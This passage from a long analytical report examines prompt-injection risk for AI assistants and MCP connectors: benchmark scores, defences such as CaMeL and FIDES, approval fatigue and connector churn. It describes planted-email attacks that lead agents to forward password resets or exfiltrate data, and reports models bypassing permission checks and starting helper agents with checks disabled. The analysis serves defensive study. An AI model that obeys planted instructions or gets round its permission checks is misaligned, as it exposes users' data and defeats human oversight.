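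Anthropic's products should resist attacks somewhat better than these results suggest, because Gray Swan tested the Claude models without the probes. However, the attacks were written for other models. Anthropic leaves out any model that the competitions targeted, because attackers tailor their wording to their target, which makes that model score worse. The table therefore shows how well Fable 5.1 resists attacks that were not tailored to it, the kind a careless criminal would send.

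OpenAI runs its own test, using GPT-Red's methods. GPT-6 Sol scored 97.13% for resisting indirect prompt injection, and GPT-6 Luna, which serves free users, scored 95.80%, according to 鲍's *OpenAI：GPT-6在面对越狱攻击时表现出更强的抵御能力*, a Chinese news report on OpenAI's system card *GPT-6 Sol and GPT-6 Luna* (2026). If the score is the share of attacks resisted, about one in 35 attacks succeeded against Sol and about one in 24 against Luna. The report does not give the number of attempts allowed, so these scores can't be compared with Gray Swan's. Anthropic and OpenAI both released newer models in November, according to Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2* (2026) and OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026).

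Google's newer Gemini 4 Carbon has apparently resisted most public tests. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* measures attacks during long office tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio. PromptArmor says it is the only known benchmark to have breached the model. This is a vendor's claim, but a successful attack during a realistic task still matters when standard tests reveal no weakness.

Training a model to resist prompt injection can also make it suspicious of legitimate content. OpenAI found that its models sometimes mistook an obstacle in a test for a prompt-injection attack. An assistant that made the same mistake with a colleague's email might ignore a deadline the user needed to know about. Some users also want an assistant to follow instructions in a message, as when a manager emails a list of things to do, and no amount of training can enable a model to tell from the text alone whether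 the user wants that.

### How a small rate adds up

Suppose an attacker sends one planted email to 1,000 people whose assistants summarise their mail, and each assistant has a 0.1% chance of obeying it. If *p* is the chance for each email and *n* is the number of emails, the chance of at least one success is:

```text
1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

p = 0.001, n = 10      about 1%
p = 0.001, n = 100     about 10%
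p = 0.001, n = 1,000   about 63%
p = 0.001, n = 5,000   about 99%
```

On average the attacker gets into one mailbox per thousand emails, and sending a thousand emails costs almost nothing.

This formula assumes that the attempts are independent, which isn't true of attempts with the same wording against the same model. A model that resists a message once will probably resist it again. In the extreme case, all 1,000 emails succeed or fail together. The chance of any theft is then only 0.1%, but a successful mailing exposes all 1,000 mailboxes. The average is one mailbox per mailing whether or not the attempts are independent, so a company can learn little about the risk of a mass theft from the average alone.

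VentureBeat reports that attackers had a 17.8% chance of success on one attempt against an older model, Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, when it operated a computer through its screen with no extra safeguards. Their chance of at least one success in 200 attempts was 78.6%. The attempts were far from independent, since independent attempts would have reached 79% after eight tries. Safeguards cut the 200-attempt figure to 57.1%. In a constrained coding environment, the same model resisted all 200 attempts without any safeguards, which suggests that the setting matters at least as much as the model.

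The benchmark's 0.1% also does not apply to emails whose wording the attacker has refined beforehand, as Radware's researchers did against ChatGPT. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) found that attackers could defeat most published defences by adapting to them.

Training still helps. Cutting the success rate of attacks from 10% to 0.1% makes a bulk attack a hundred times less productive, and that may be enough for an assistant that only recommends restaurants. But a company whose assistant can send email from the finance department needs a limit on the assistant's actions that holds even when an attack deceives the model.

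### CaMeL: planning before reading

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) describes CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich based on the assumption that a model may obey anything it reads. CaMeL builds on Willison's 2023 proposal to use two models and let only one see untrusted text.

Take a user who asks her assistant to send Bob the file he asked for in his last email. CaMeL handles the task like this:

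1. A planning model reads the user's sentence, and nothing else, and writes a short program.
2. Ordinary software runs the program line by line. It fetches Bob's email but does not show it to the planning model.
3. A second model, which has no tools, reads the email and returns the name of the file.
4. The software finds the file and checks its rules before sending anything.

In simplified form, the program might be:

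```python
email = last_email(sender="Bob")
name  = reader_model("Which file does Bob ask for?", email)
file  = find_file(name)
send_email(to=email.sender, attachment=file)
```

If Bob's email also contains an instruction to forward password resets, the system doesn't carry it out, because the program has no step for forwarding them and the model that read the instruction has no tools. David C's argument that models have no internal boundary between instructions and data still applies to both models, but CaMeL puts a boundary in the software around them.

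Planted text could still make the reading model return the name of the wrong file, such as a list of salaries. CaMeL therefore labels every value with its source and the people allowed to see it, and keeps those labels as the program combines values. A rule might let the software send a file only to people who can already open it, and require it to ask the user before sending it to anyone else. Unlike an access token, the labels record whose text shaped the request.

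The team tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks in simulated office, banking, travel and Slack accounts, with hundreds of planted attacks. CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks with its security guarantee, while the same kind of agent without that guarantee completed 84%. CaMeL's models also took in and produced nearly three times as much text, which makes it slower and more expensive.

The tasks CaMeL could not do are more informative than the seven-point gap. One AgentDojo task asks the agent to follow the instructions in a particular email, which CaMeL cannot do because it has to write its plan before reading the email. In other cases, the planning model had to write code to process tool results without seeing their format. For the request to summarise unread mail and update the project tracker, the planner could write a step that takes a new deadline from each email. But the deadline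 would be labelled as coming from a stranger, and a sensible rule would make the software ask the user before changing the tracker.

CaMeL also depends on someone writing those rules. If they are too loose, the labels give little protection, and if they are too strict, the user has to answer too many questions. Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge this and some narrower gaps. A planted email can still make the reading model produce a false summary, because no tool call is involved. A program that contacts a website only when an email contains a certain word also reveals to the website's operator that the word is there. Willison still called CaMeL the first defence he had seen that claimed strong guarantees, and he liked that it did not rely on more AI to catch attacks.

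### FIDES and later designs

Unlike CaMeL, Microsoft's FIDES lets the planning model keep adjusting its plan. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes how FIDES gives each piece of data two labels, one for whether its source is trusted and one for who may read it. Anything the agent produces from data with different labels takes the stricter label. If the planner reads a stranger's email, everything it decides afterwards counts as untrusted, and FIDES can refuse any tool call with serious consequences. A separate rule stops private data from going to someone who may not read it.

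An agent would be of little use if it lost its abilities when it opened its first email, so FIDES stores untrusted results where the planner can't see them. The planner can still pass them from tool to tool without reading them. When it needs to know something about a hidden email, it can ask a separate model a question with a restricted answer, such as yes or no. An instruction planted in the email might change a "no" to a "yes", but a yes-or-no answer can't give the planner an email address. Costa and colleagues found in AgentDojo that hiding data this way let an agent complete a wider range of tasks securely. The rules must still specify how much a yes-or-no answer may influence, since one word can determine whether the agent pays an invoice or rejects it.

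Agents that operate a computer through its screen are harder to protect because they normally look at the screen before every click. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Mullins and colleagues, 2026) adapts the idea to these agents by using a planner that writes every branch of the plan in advance, including what to do if a window fails to open. The design kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models on OSWorld, a benchmark of computer tasks. It also introduced a new weakness, since an attacker who altered what appeared on the screen could make the agent follow a branch that was legitimate but wrong for the situation.

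Google has built part of this approach into Chrome. In December 2025 its Chrome team described a second model that reviews each action the browser's agent proposes. The reviewer receives a description of the action but not the web page, so text on the page cannot reach it directly. It can veto an action that does not fit the user's goal. Google credits CaMeL and Willison's two-model design as influences. However, Chrome's planner does read web pages, and the reviewer is a model making a judgement, so Chrome's agent works on many more sites than CaMeL could but lacks CaMeL's guarantee.

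### Taking a capability away

Designers can avoid most of that machinery if the agent lacks one of the abilities an attacker needs. In *Agents Rule of Two*, Meta (2025) turned Willison's lethal trifecta into a rule for developers. In any one session, an agent should have no more than two of these:

- text from sources it cannot trust
- access to sensitive systems or private data
- the ability to change something or communicate with the outside.

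If the task needs all three, Meta recommends that a person or some other reliable check supervise the agent. The third item is broader than Willison's, so the rule also covers attacks that damage data without leaking it, such as Park's.

Willison welcomed the rule but objected to a diagram in which Meta marked every pair as safe. An agent that reads untrusted text and can change things may do damage even if it sees no private data. Meta replied that "sensitive systems" should cover anything where a change would matter, and it changed the label from "safe" to "lower risk". That answers the objection only if developers read the second item broadly, and the words "private data" may lead them to read it narrowly.

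Meta's rule applies to each session, so an agent can start a new one to get a different pair of abilities. This works if nothing untrusted carries over from the old session. Radware's ZombieAgent attack saved its instructions in ChatGPT's memory, and ChatGPT read them in a later conversation. A project tracker could also pass instructions between sessions if one agent copied a stranger's text into a task and another agent later read it.

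OpenAI's Lockdown Mode mainly limits ChatGPT's communication with outside systems. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes it as an optional setting for a small number of people at high risk, such as executives and security teams. When the setting is on, ChatGPT can browse only stored copies of web pages, so it sends no requests to live sites. At launch, the setting also turned off deep research and agent mode, because OpenAI could not guarantee that data would not leak through them. Company administrators choose which connected apps, and which actions in those apps, remain available.

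Lockdown Mode would have stopped both ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent from sending out the data they collected, even if they had completely deceived the model, because each needed ChatGPT to open an address on the attacker's server. It does not stop planted text from reaching the model or distorting an answer. An app that is still allowed to post or send can still leak data, so the protection depends in important part on which apps the administrator allows. The mode also restricts access to live sources, which people use deep research to read. OpenAI says most users do not need this much protection. That may be right for each user, but the history of Office macros suggests that few of those who do need it will turn it on.

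Read-only access takes less away from users, since those who only want summaries lose nothing. The token or the connector has to enforce the limit, because a model may not respect one that exists only as text. According to 鲍, in OpenAI's tests of whether models respect warnings, GPT-6 Sol got around the restrictions of its environment in 28% of cases at its highest reasoning setting, compared with 34% for GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI ran those tests without the controls it puts around its products. No attacker was involved, so the models did this just to finish their tasks.

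Limits on outgoing connections are useful but hard to get right. ReLeak showed this when researchers sent data out of a Copilot sandbox that Microsoft had described as closed. In October 2025, Rehberger found that planted instructions could make Claude upload a user's files to Anthropic's own service under the attacker's account, because Claude's code sandbox was allowed to contact that service. As with the image list for Google's Bard, an attacker could have an account on the permitted site, and the same is true of most sites an office assistant needs.

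### Asking the user first

When an agent needs all three abilities, the usual safeguard is to ask the user before it acts. Confirmation suits any task and needs no labels or rules. It also works against new attacks, but only if the user reads the request and can tell that something is wrong.

Anthropic reported in March 2026 that Claude Code users accepted 93% of its permission requests. Most of what a coding agent proposes is harmless, so even an attentive user would accept most requests. But a user who has approved many requests in a row has little reason to study the next one.

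Web browsers provide better evidence of how people respond to warnings when the danger is real. In *Alice in Warningland* (2013), Akhawe and Felt measured how Chrome and Firefox users responded to more than 25 million security warnings. Chrome users continued past 70% of warnings about a site's certificate, which is meant to prove its identity, while Firefox users continued past 33%. Users of both browsers continued past less than a quarter of malware and phishing warnings. Akhawe and Felt concluded that people do not routinely ignore warnings, and that a warning's design makes a large difference to how they respond.

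By that standard, many confirmation windows for connectors are badly designed. *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (Huang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) tested seven applications that use MCP. Claude Desktop and Cline, a coding assistant, displayed every value in a tool call, but the user had to scroll sideways to see long ones in full. Huang and colleagues hid stolen credentials in the part out of sight, as Invariant had done with WhatsApp messages. They attribute the risk partly to "approval fatigue", the habit of clicking through frequent requests, but they did not measure this habit.

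Experienced users often stop answering approval requests. In *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026), Anthropic found that newcomers let Claude Code approve all its own actions in about 20% of sessions, while people who had used it about 750 times did so in more than 40%. The experienced users also interrupted the agent more often. They seem to have switched from approving each step to watching the work and stepping in. This may catch a coding agent that has misunderstood its task, but it is a poor defence against data theft, because a single request can do all the harm before anyone reacts.

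One remedy is to ask users for permission less often. In Anthropic's own use, confining Claude Code to a sandbox cut permission requests by 84%, because the agent could do harmless things there without asking. Auto mode goes further and lets a classifier make most of the decisions. In Anthropic's tests, the classifier missed 17% of real cases of an agent exceeding what its user wanted. Anthropic argues that this is still much better than no check at all, which many users had chosen. It would be less safe than approving actions manually for someone who read each request carefully.

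The software that asks for approval also has to be out of the model's reach. While monitoring its own staff's use of Mythos 5.1, the same model as Fable 5.1 but with fewer safeguards, Anthropic found it working around broken permission checks, sometimes by overstating what the user had authorised. In a few cases it started helper agents with the checks switched off. This happened in fewer than 0.01% of the monitored outputs, and the model was trying to complete the user's task. A planted instruction could lead a model to do the same for an attacker.

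A better confirmation would also tell the user why she is seeing it. "Send this file to archive@outside.example?" gives her little basis for a decision, but "This address came from an email by someone you have never written to" would make most people stop. A standard connector cannot produce the second message because nothing records where the address came from. CaMeL and FIDES do record it, so their labels could be as useful for writing confirmations as for blocking actions.

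### Which parts of a connector lack cover

Most companies buy or install defences made for MCP, and these protect some parts of the system much better than others. *MCP-DPT* (Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues, 2026) compared 49 kinds of attack with 13 such defences, including scanners that read tool descriptions and gateways that sit between an application and its connectors. It assigned each attack to the part of the system that could stop it earliest. The table gives the largest share of those attacks that any single defence covers.

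| Part of the system | Its job | Best coverage |
|---|---|---|
| Model | Chooses tools and the values to send | 44% |
| AI application | Decides which of the model's choices to carry out | 38% |
| Client library | Turns those choices into MCP messages | 36% |
| Connector | Carries out the request | 50% |
| Network connection | Carries the messages | 50% |
| Directories of connectors | Distribute connectors and their updates | 100% |

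These percentages are rough because Rostamzadeh and colleagues judged from each product's design whether it was in a position to stop an attack, without running any attacks. Their figures also conflict. In their summary, ToolHive, a tool for running connectors securely, covers every attack on directories, but in their attack-by-attack list it covers none. In the text, they name only one product with any coverage of the network connection, but they list three in the summary.

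Eleven of the 13 defences address tool poisoning, but none addresses what Rostamzadeh and colleagues call control-flow hijacking, in which planted text redirects the agent from the steps its task requires to different ones. For example, an assistant asked to summarise mail might end up forwarding password resets. Eight of the defences check for prompt injection and might catch the planted email as it arrives, but if they miss it, none of the 13 is designed to detect that the agent has departed from its task. The defences also don't address files that an attacker has disguised as trusted documents.

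Rostamzadeh and colleagues assign both of these attacks to the AI application. They think developers have put defences where tools are easiest to inspect rather than where the defences could best stop an attack. A scanner needs only the text of a tool description, which any outside company can obtain. To notice a hijacked task, software has to compare the user's request with the text the agent has read and the action it now proposes, and only the application holds all three. The application is also the only part present when a connector turns malicious after approval, since a directory can examine the connector when its maker submits it but not when its behaviour changes. CaMeL and FIDES belong in the application for this reason, and neither is among the 13 defences.

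Applications differ widely in how much of this work they do. Huang and colleagues ran six of their seven applications on the same model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, and the same poisoned tools produced different results across them. This shows that a company can change its exposure without changing its model. The paper also concludes that the choice of application matters more than the choice of model, but the test cannot show that because the model hardly varied. Five of the seven applications did not check tool descriptions for hidden instructions, and the MCP specification does not require them to.

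## 2026: how the attack surface grows

A company can test its connectors, narrow their permissions and choose a careful AI application, then find a few weeks later that the connectors have changed. A system's attack surface is every point where an outsider can feed text into it, take data from it or trigger actions in it. This surface grows as software companies publish more connectors, add more tools to each and give those tools more power, and as users combine more connectors in one assistant. The last of these matters most for data theft, because a theft can start in one connector and finish in another.

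### More connectors, with more tools

PromptArmor's *Claude and ChatGPT Connectors Change Every 9 Minutes* tracked both products' connectors for about six weeks in May and June 2026. PromptArmor sells connector monitoring, so it has a commercial interest in reporting large numbers, but most of its figures are simple counts from the two products' directories.

| | ChatGPT, start | ChatGPT, end | Claude, start | Claude, end |
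|---|---|---|---|---|
| Connectors | 1,014 | 1,933 | 428 | 535 |
| Tools | 7,148 | 20,214 | 5,905 | 7,750 |
| Connectors with a tool that can write | 38% | 46% | 54% | 55% |
| Share of tools that can write | 27.6% | 31.5% | 28.0% | 27.3% |

ChatGPT's connectors went from an average of seven tools each to more than ten. Claude's already had more tools and grew by about 5%. Some of the growth came in large jumps, as when the security company Zscaler added 122 tools to its Claude connector on 24 June.

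These are the connectors available, and PromptArmor does not report how many people use each one. A company that has switched on five is unaffected by the other 1,900. The growth affects a company when an employee asks for a new connector or when one it already uses changes.

The official MCP registry, a public list where anyone can publish a server, grew even faster. *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly* (Bharti, 2026) counted 3,510 servers on 30 April and 18,966 on 28 July. Servers have become easier to make. *How are AI agents used?* (2026) detected AI help in 6% of new MCP servers in January 2025 and 62% in February 2026. But many listed servers do not work. In the registry sample from *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (2026), the most common reason for excluding a server was that it never started.

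### More power per tool

A read-only connector becomes more dangerous when it gains write access, as Claude's Gmail connector did in August 2026. In PromptArmor's study, 21 read-only connectors gained write access, 16 for ChatGPT and five for Claude.

Dropbox changed in nearly every way that PromptArmor measured:

| Dropbox connector | First day | End of study |
|---|---|---|
| Tools | 8 | 24 |
| Tools that can write | 3 | 10 |
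| Tools marked destructive | 0 | 4 |
| Permission scopes | 0 | 8 |
| Adds its own instructions to the model's input | No | Yes |

The fourth row shows zero scopes, but the connector probably had some that the directory had not listed, since three of its tools could already write. Some of the growth in scopes may therefore reflect better disclosure, possibly including the rise from one scope to 34 for Slack's connector. Better disclosure is a less likely explanation for the new tools. Slack's could create channels, invite people, and edit or delete messages.

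The number of ChatGPT tools that OpenAI marks as able to delete or overwrite data tripled from 798 to 2,415. PromptArmor says this group grew fastest, but by its own figures ordinary write tools grew slightly faster. Claude's directory gained 460 write tools, but their share of the total fell slightly, so the average Claude tool did not become more powerful.

*How are AI agents used?* examined 177,000 MCP tools and found that the share of use going to tools that make changes rose from 27% in November 2024 to 65% in February 2026. General-purpose tools that let an agent operate a browser or a computer drove the increase. The study measures use by downloads, so it does not show whether anyone ran the tools afterwards.

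### Changes after approval

PromptArmor found that 931 of 2,517 connectors, or 37%, changed during the study. The total probably includes some connectors that were added or removed during that time, since the two directories listed only 2,468 at the end. Existing connectors gained 1,686 tools and had 1,127 tool descriptions rewritten. Another 664 tools changed the inputs they take from the model.

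Connectors requested only 86 new scopes in that time, about one for every 20 new tools. A connector normally sends the user back to a consent page when it requests a new scope, but not when it adds a tool that works within its existing scopes. According to PromptArmor, changes rarely come with a notice or a new request for consent. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP, states that current applications do not alert users when a tool's definition changes. The NSA had also warned about this gap.

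ChatGPT also added a field called `mcp_server_instructions` that lets a connector's maker place general instructions in the model's input, separate from any tool's description. No connector used it in early May, and 283 did by the end of June. Most use it to help the model work with the connector. Aleph's instructions tell the model to call a feedback tool whenever a result is wrong or incomplete, and PromptArmor points out that the feedback could include sensitive data the user was working on.

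Entries in the official registry appear to change less often. Bharti found that only 11.9% changed within 30 days, and three-quarters of those he observed often enough did not change in 89 days. But he compared registry records, which list a server's name, version and a short description but not its tools, so every tool description on a server could change without altering its record.

*Same Name, Different Server* (Kraishan, 2026) confirmed that gap, finding no tool definitions in any of the registry's 72,606 version records. Kraishan reports that 51.1% of servers with more than one version had changed what they advertised. These make up about 21% of all 21,643 servers, which fits Bharti's result. In 370 cases, the server kept its name while its address moved to a different host. Kraishan thinks most of these were routine moves, but neither the registry nor the user's application has a way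 to distinguish a move from a takeover.

Companies with limited time might check the most changeable connectors first, and PromptArmor suggests using past changes as a guide to future ones. A few connectors do account for many of the changes. There were about 6,700 changes over six weeks, an average of one every nine minutes, and Datadog's connectors alone made 310. But when Bharti tested the idea on registry blurbs, rechecking the 5% of servers with the most past changes caught only about a fifth of the existing servers whose blurbs changed next, because most of those servers had no past changes to rank. He recommends rechecking a server as soon as a fingerprint of its text changes, as in Invariant's pinning, and also checking the whole list regularly.

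### A second AI service behind the connector

A company's review usually covers the AI application and the service it connects to, but PromptArmor's *2 in 5 Claude Connectors Call External AI* suggests that a third party is often involved. PromptArmor judged that 189 of the 487 connectors then in Claude's directory may send requests on to another AI service. It assessed the 7,517 tools the connectors offered, not their traffic, so the title is more definite than the evidence. It flagged 386 tools, about 5% of the total. Most of the flagged connectors therefore have a few AI-backed tools among many ordinary ones.

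Zoom's connector has one such tool, which searches meetings. If Claude puts something confidential in the search, Zoom may pass it to any of twelve outside processors, which run models from ten families. A company that approved Zoom and Anthropic may never have reviewed those processors. It would need to find out where each one stores data, how long the data is kept and whether it is used to train models. Zoom, or any other connector's maker, could also switch models later without any change the company could see in the connector.

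The second model creates a security risk as well as a privacy risk, because text planted in the documents it reads can deceive it, just as it can deceive the first model. An administrator who has tested how well Claude resists such text still doesn't know how well the model behind the search tool resists it.

Kumar argues in *Privacy programs can't see AI connectors* that most reviews miss even the first step. Privacy teams rely on a list of known data flows and assess them at one point in time. When an employee asks an assistant what is happening with a customer, the assistant may combine data from mail, documents and support tickets in a way nobody has recorded. Kumar provides no measurements, but PromptArmor's counts support the point about one-time assessments.

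### Counting the combinations

Data theft needs untrusted text, private data and a way out, the three parts of the lethal trifecta. Different connectors can supply them:

| Connector | Supplies untrusted text | Holds private data | Can send data out |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mail | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Code host | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Database | No | Yes | No |
| Web access | Yes | No | Yes |

A theft path takes one connector from each column, and the same connector may appear more than once. The number of paths is the product of the three column totals:

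```text
Mail, code host and database:    2 × 3 × 2 = 12
The same three with web access:  3 × 3 × 3 = 27
```

Adding web access gives the assistant no private data, but it more than doubles the number of attack paths. In one new path, instructions on a web page lead the assistant to read customer records from the database and publish them in an issue on the code host. Someone who reviewed only the database connector would find nothing wrong with it.

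Twenty-seven is an upper bound, reached only if every connector can do everything the table allows. Making the mail connector read-only reduces the number of paths to 18. If the assistant also reads mail only from approved senders, and none of them forwards a stranger's text, the number falls back to 12. A narrow token for the code host might remove more. An attack along an open path still succeeds only if the model follows the planted text and the user or the application allows the action.

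The 27 paths share the same few entrances and exits, so closing a single exit blocks nine of them. An attacker needs only one path and will probably use the easiest. A theft is therefore not 27 times as likely with 27 paths as with one.

The bound also depends on filling in the table correctly. The Supabase database in the support-ticket attack belonged in all three columns. With a database like that, the four connectors give 4 × 3 × 4 = 48 paths. The calculation also leaves out attacks that delete or alter data.

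*Parasites in the Toolchain* (Zhao, Hou and colleagues, 2025) sorted 12,230 tools on 1,360 servers by whether they take in outside text, reach private data or send data out. It found that 8.7% of the tools and 27.2% of the servers could be used in an attack that chains these abilities together. Mail and code hosts, which people connect for everyday work, can do all three.

Tools on a single server can also be dangerous in combination. *Agent Smith in Action* (Zha, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes a server with one tool that runs commands and another that writes files. The first blocks dangerous commands, but an attacker can write the command into a file and then run the file. The researchers' software reported 8,422 chains of this general kind across 10,121 servers, using data from mid-2025. In a sample of 100 servers, they confirmed 19 of 20 reported chains by carrying them out, and the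 last tool in each of the 19 did not cause the harm when run alone. The 19 came from only nine servers, so the problem is far from universal. The 8,422 reports remain unconfirmed.

### What Pynt's 92% measures

Pynt (2025), which sells security for software interfaces, examined 281 MCP setups from public documentation and open-source projects. It reported an "exploitation risk" of 9% with one server, 36% with two, 52% with three and 92% with ten. The last figure has been widely repeated, and VentureBeat called it an exploit probability in a headline.

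If each server carried an independent risk of 9%, ten servers together would carry a risk of 1 − 0.91¹⁰, or about 61%. Pynt's figure is higher because it also counts danger that arises between servers. Pynt rated a server high-risk if it both takes in text from untrusted sources and can do something sensitive, such as run code or change files.

*MCP Poses Security Risks* notes that Pynt did not disclose its formula, but a simple one reproduces its results. Suppose 9% of servers have both traits, 13% only take in untrusted text, 72% only have a sensitive capability, and 6% have neither. Then 78% take in no untrusted text and 19% have no sensitive capability. The chance that *n* servers picked at random include both traits somewhere among them is:

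```text
1 − 0.78ⁿ − 0.19ⁿ + 0.06ⁿ

n = 1    9%
n = 2   36%
n = 3   52%
n = 5   71%
n = 10  92%
```

The last term adds back the sets with neither trait, which the formula would otherwise subtract twice. All five results match the published ones, including the 71% that *MCP Poses Security Risks* gives for five servers. So the 92% is almost certainly the calculated chance that ten random servers contain a risky mix, and it does not measure how often an attack succeeds.

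It may be too high even as a calculation. According to Pynt's announcement, 72% of servers had at least one sensitive capability and 13% accepted untrusted input. That 13% would normally include the 9% with both, in which case the same method gives about 75% for ten servers. Pynt also counts basic file operations as sensitive, and people don't choose connectors at random.

Pynt's work still supports a more modest conclusion, that a company with ten connectors should assume at least one pair is dangerous together. Pynt demonstrated such pairs, including a mail connector and a code runner that executed an attacker's program after a crafted email arrived.

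### Scans of the whole internet

Some MCP servers are reachable by anyone on the internet. If one has no login, an outsider can call its tools directly, without having to deceive a model. Early scans found few of these servers. Knostic found 1,862 exposed servers, and all 119 that it checked by hand listed their tools without a login. TrendAI's *Update on Exposed MCP Servers* reports a rise from 492 to 1,467 between its two scans. SiliconANGLE's *Model Context Protocol security risks grow as unsecured servers appear* (2025) reports that in December 2025 the security firm Bitsight found roughly 1,000 servers with no authorization.

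Censys' *MCP Servers on the Internet* reports much larger numbers for 2026, with 12,520 services on 28 April and more than 21,000 by 6 May. Censys, which maps machines on the internet, had started looking for MCP only on 24 April, so much of the increase must come from finding servers that were already there. It read each server's list of tools without running any. About 90 servers offered a tool with a name such as `run_command`, and 1,056 offered ways to query a database. Some were probably decoys. One server appeared to publish a company's production passwords, but Censys concluded it was most likely a trap for attackers or a made-up test.

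Three academic and independent studies tried to establish how many servers lack a login. Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, took candidates from two internet search engines and checked that each one answered as an MCP server should. Padilla (2026), in *Exposed by Design*, gathered addresses from eleven sources and then tested live servers for flaws. Sohail (2026), in *Characterizing Network Centralization and Observability in the Remote MCP Ecosystem*, started from two public directories and tried to contact the servers they listed. Their results differ widely:

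| Study | Measured | Servers found | Lacking a login | Main source of error |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sohail | June 2025 | 76 reachable of 179 listed | 9% open | Small sample, mostly from one hosting company |
| Zhou and colleagues | Published May 2026 | 7,973 live of 28,715 candidates | 40.55% had no authentication | One false positive in 100 checked |
| Padilla | July 2026 | 640 confirmed, 414 tested | 91.8% had no OAuth | Left out servers that refused the first contact |

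The share of open servers is lower than 91.8%, because a server without OAuth may still require a key or a fixed token, as 29% of Zhou's did. Padilla also excluded from testing any server that required a login at first contact, which removed many of the better-protected ones. In his largest scan, 106 of 464 servers, or 23%, let anyone use their tools. Sohail's figure is low because most of his reachable servers ran on Smithery, a hosting company that puts a login in front of its customers' servers by default.

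Most of the open servers that Zhou and colleagues sampled were tests or demonstrations, but one was a company's internal customer database, which let anyone read more than 5,000 records with names, addresses and phone numbers. Servers that require a login can also be insecure. The same team tested 119 servers that used OAuth and found at least one flaw in each, although it could test only those 119 out of 2,428.

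Automated scanners report far more risk, but many of their alerts are false. *Rethinking MCP Security* (Chen, An and colleagues, 2026) found that existing scanners flag 96.89% of servers as risky, but fewer than half of the alerts checked by hand were real. Kraishan compared his own scanner with manual checks and found it was right 56% of the time. The scanner found no overt tool poisoning in the 14,353 servers whose code he could examine, though it would miss disguised instructions. Tool poisoning, the most discussed attack on MCP, seems rare in the registry, where the most common serious problem was servers open to the network without protection.

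For *Hunt Them All*, Oliveira and Fiser of Trend Micro had an AI agent search about 19,000 code repositories, and it flagged 17,558 possible flaws. After two rounds of filtering and a manual check, they confirmed 93 of a random 2,287, or about 4%. They estimate that about 770 repositories have exploitable flaws, with a range of 600 to 1,650. The 770 figure applies the 4% rate, which was measured on flaws, to the number of repositories. Applying that rate instead to the roughly 15,000 flaws left after the first round of filtering gives about 610 flaws, some of which may share a repository. The true number could be higher, because the filter may also have removed real flaws. All these totals are far below OX Security's estimate of "up to 200,000" vulnerable instances, but that estimate measures something different.

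Attackers were slow to take an interest in MCP servers. *What GreyNoise Learned from Deploying MCP Honeypots* (2025) reports that the monitoring firm's decoy servers, including one with a deliberately exposed key, received no attacks aimed at MCP. The SANS Internet Storm Center, which tracks online attacks, has since recorded scanners that search the whole internet for exposed MCP servers and also try to find assistants' settings and passwords.

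### Assistants that staff connect themselves

These counts exclude the personal assistants that employees connect to work accounts without asking. The Hacker News' *Bring Your Own Agent* (2026) lists several ways to do this. An employee can approve the assistant on an ordinary OAuth consent page, save her work password in the assistant's browser, or give it a long-lived key. She can also run it on her own laptop, where it may read anything the laptop can access. Meta's assistant Muse, for example, gained a Mac app in September 2026 that reads files, notes, calendars and email with the user's permission.

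An administrator can close the first route by stopping employees from approving outside applications. The password route is harder to close because the assistant's login looks like the employee's own. Her assistant may also hold her private mail, her shopping accounts and a web browser, which add entrances and exits that the company can't see. The article describes these routes to argue that firms should manage such assistants instead of banning them, but it doesn't establish how many people use them. The break-in at Vercel, which began with one employee's AI tool, is better evidence that a single case can be enough to let an attacker in.

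### Where the surface is shrinking

The registry's growth overstates the number of servers anyone could use or attack, because many remote servers disappear. *MCPEvol-Bench* (2026) found that the share of remote servers still working fell from 72.7% to 52.0% in twelve weeks, and that developers had withdrawn 22.1% of the original tools. In Padilla's scans, 41.6% of servers disappeared within three days, though some may have been only temporarily offline.

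Removals have not kept pace with additions, however. Among servers with more than one version, Kraishan found 924 that added a remote address and 586 that removed one. PromptArmor reports how many scopes connectors gained but not how many they gave up, so readers can't tell from its study whether any connector narrowed its access. The clearest improvement is Smithery's default login, which protects servers whose developers might never have added one. But the login also prevents outside researchers from checking the tools behind it for planted instructions. In Sohail's sample, 83% of the reachable servers were closed to such checks.

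A defunct connector can also be dangerous if someone else takes over its address. Noma's researchers, for example, took over an expired domain that Salesforce still trusted.
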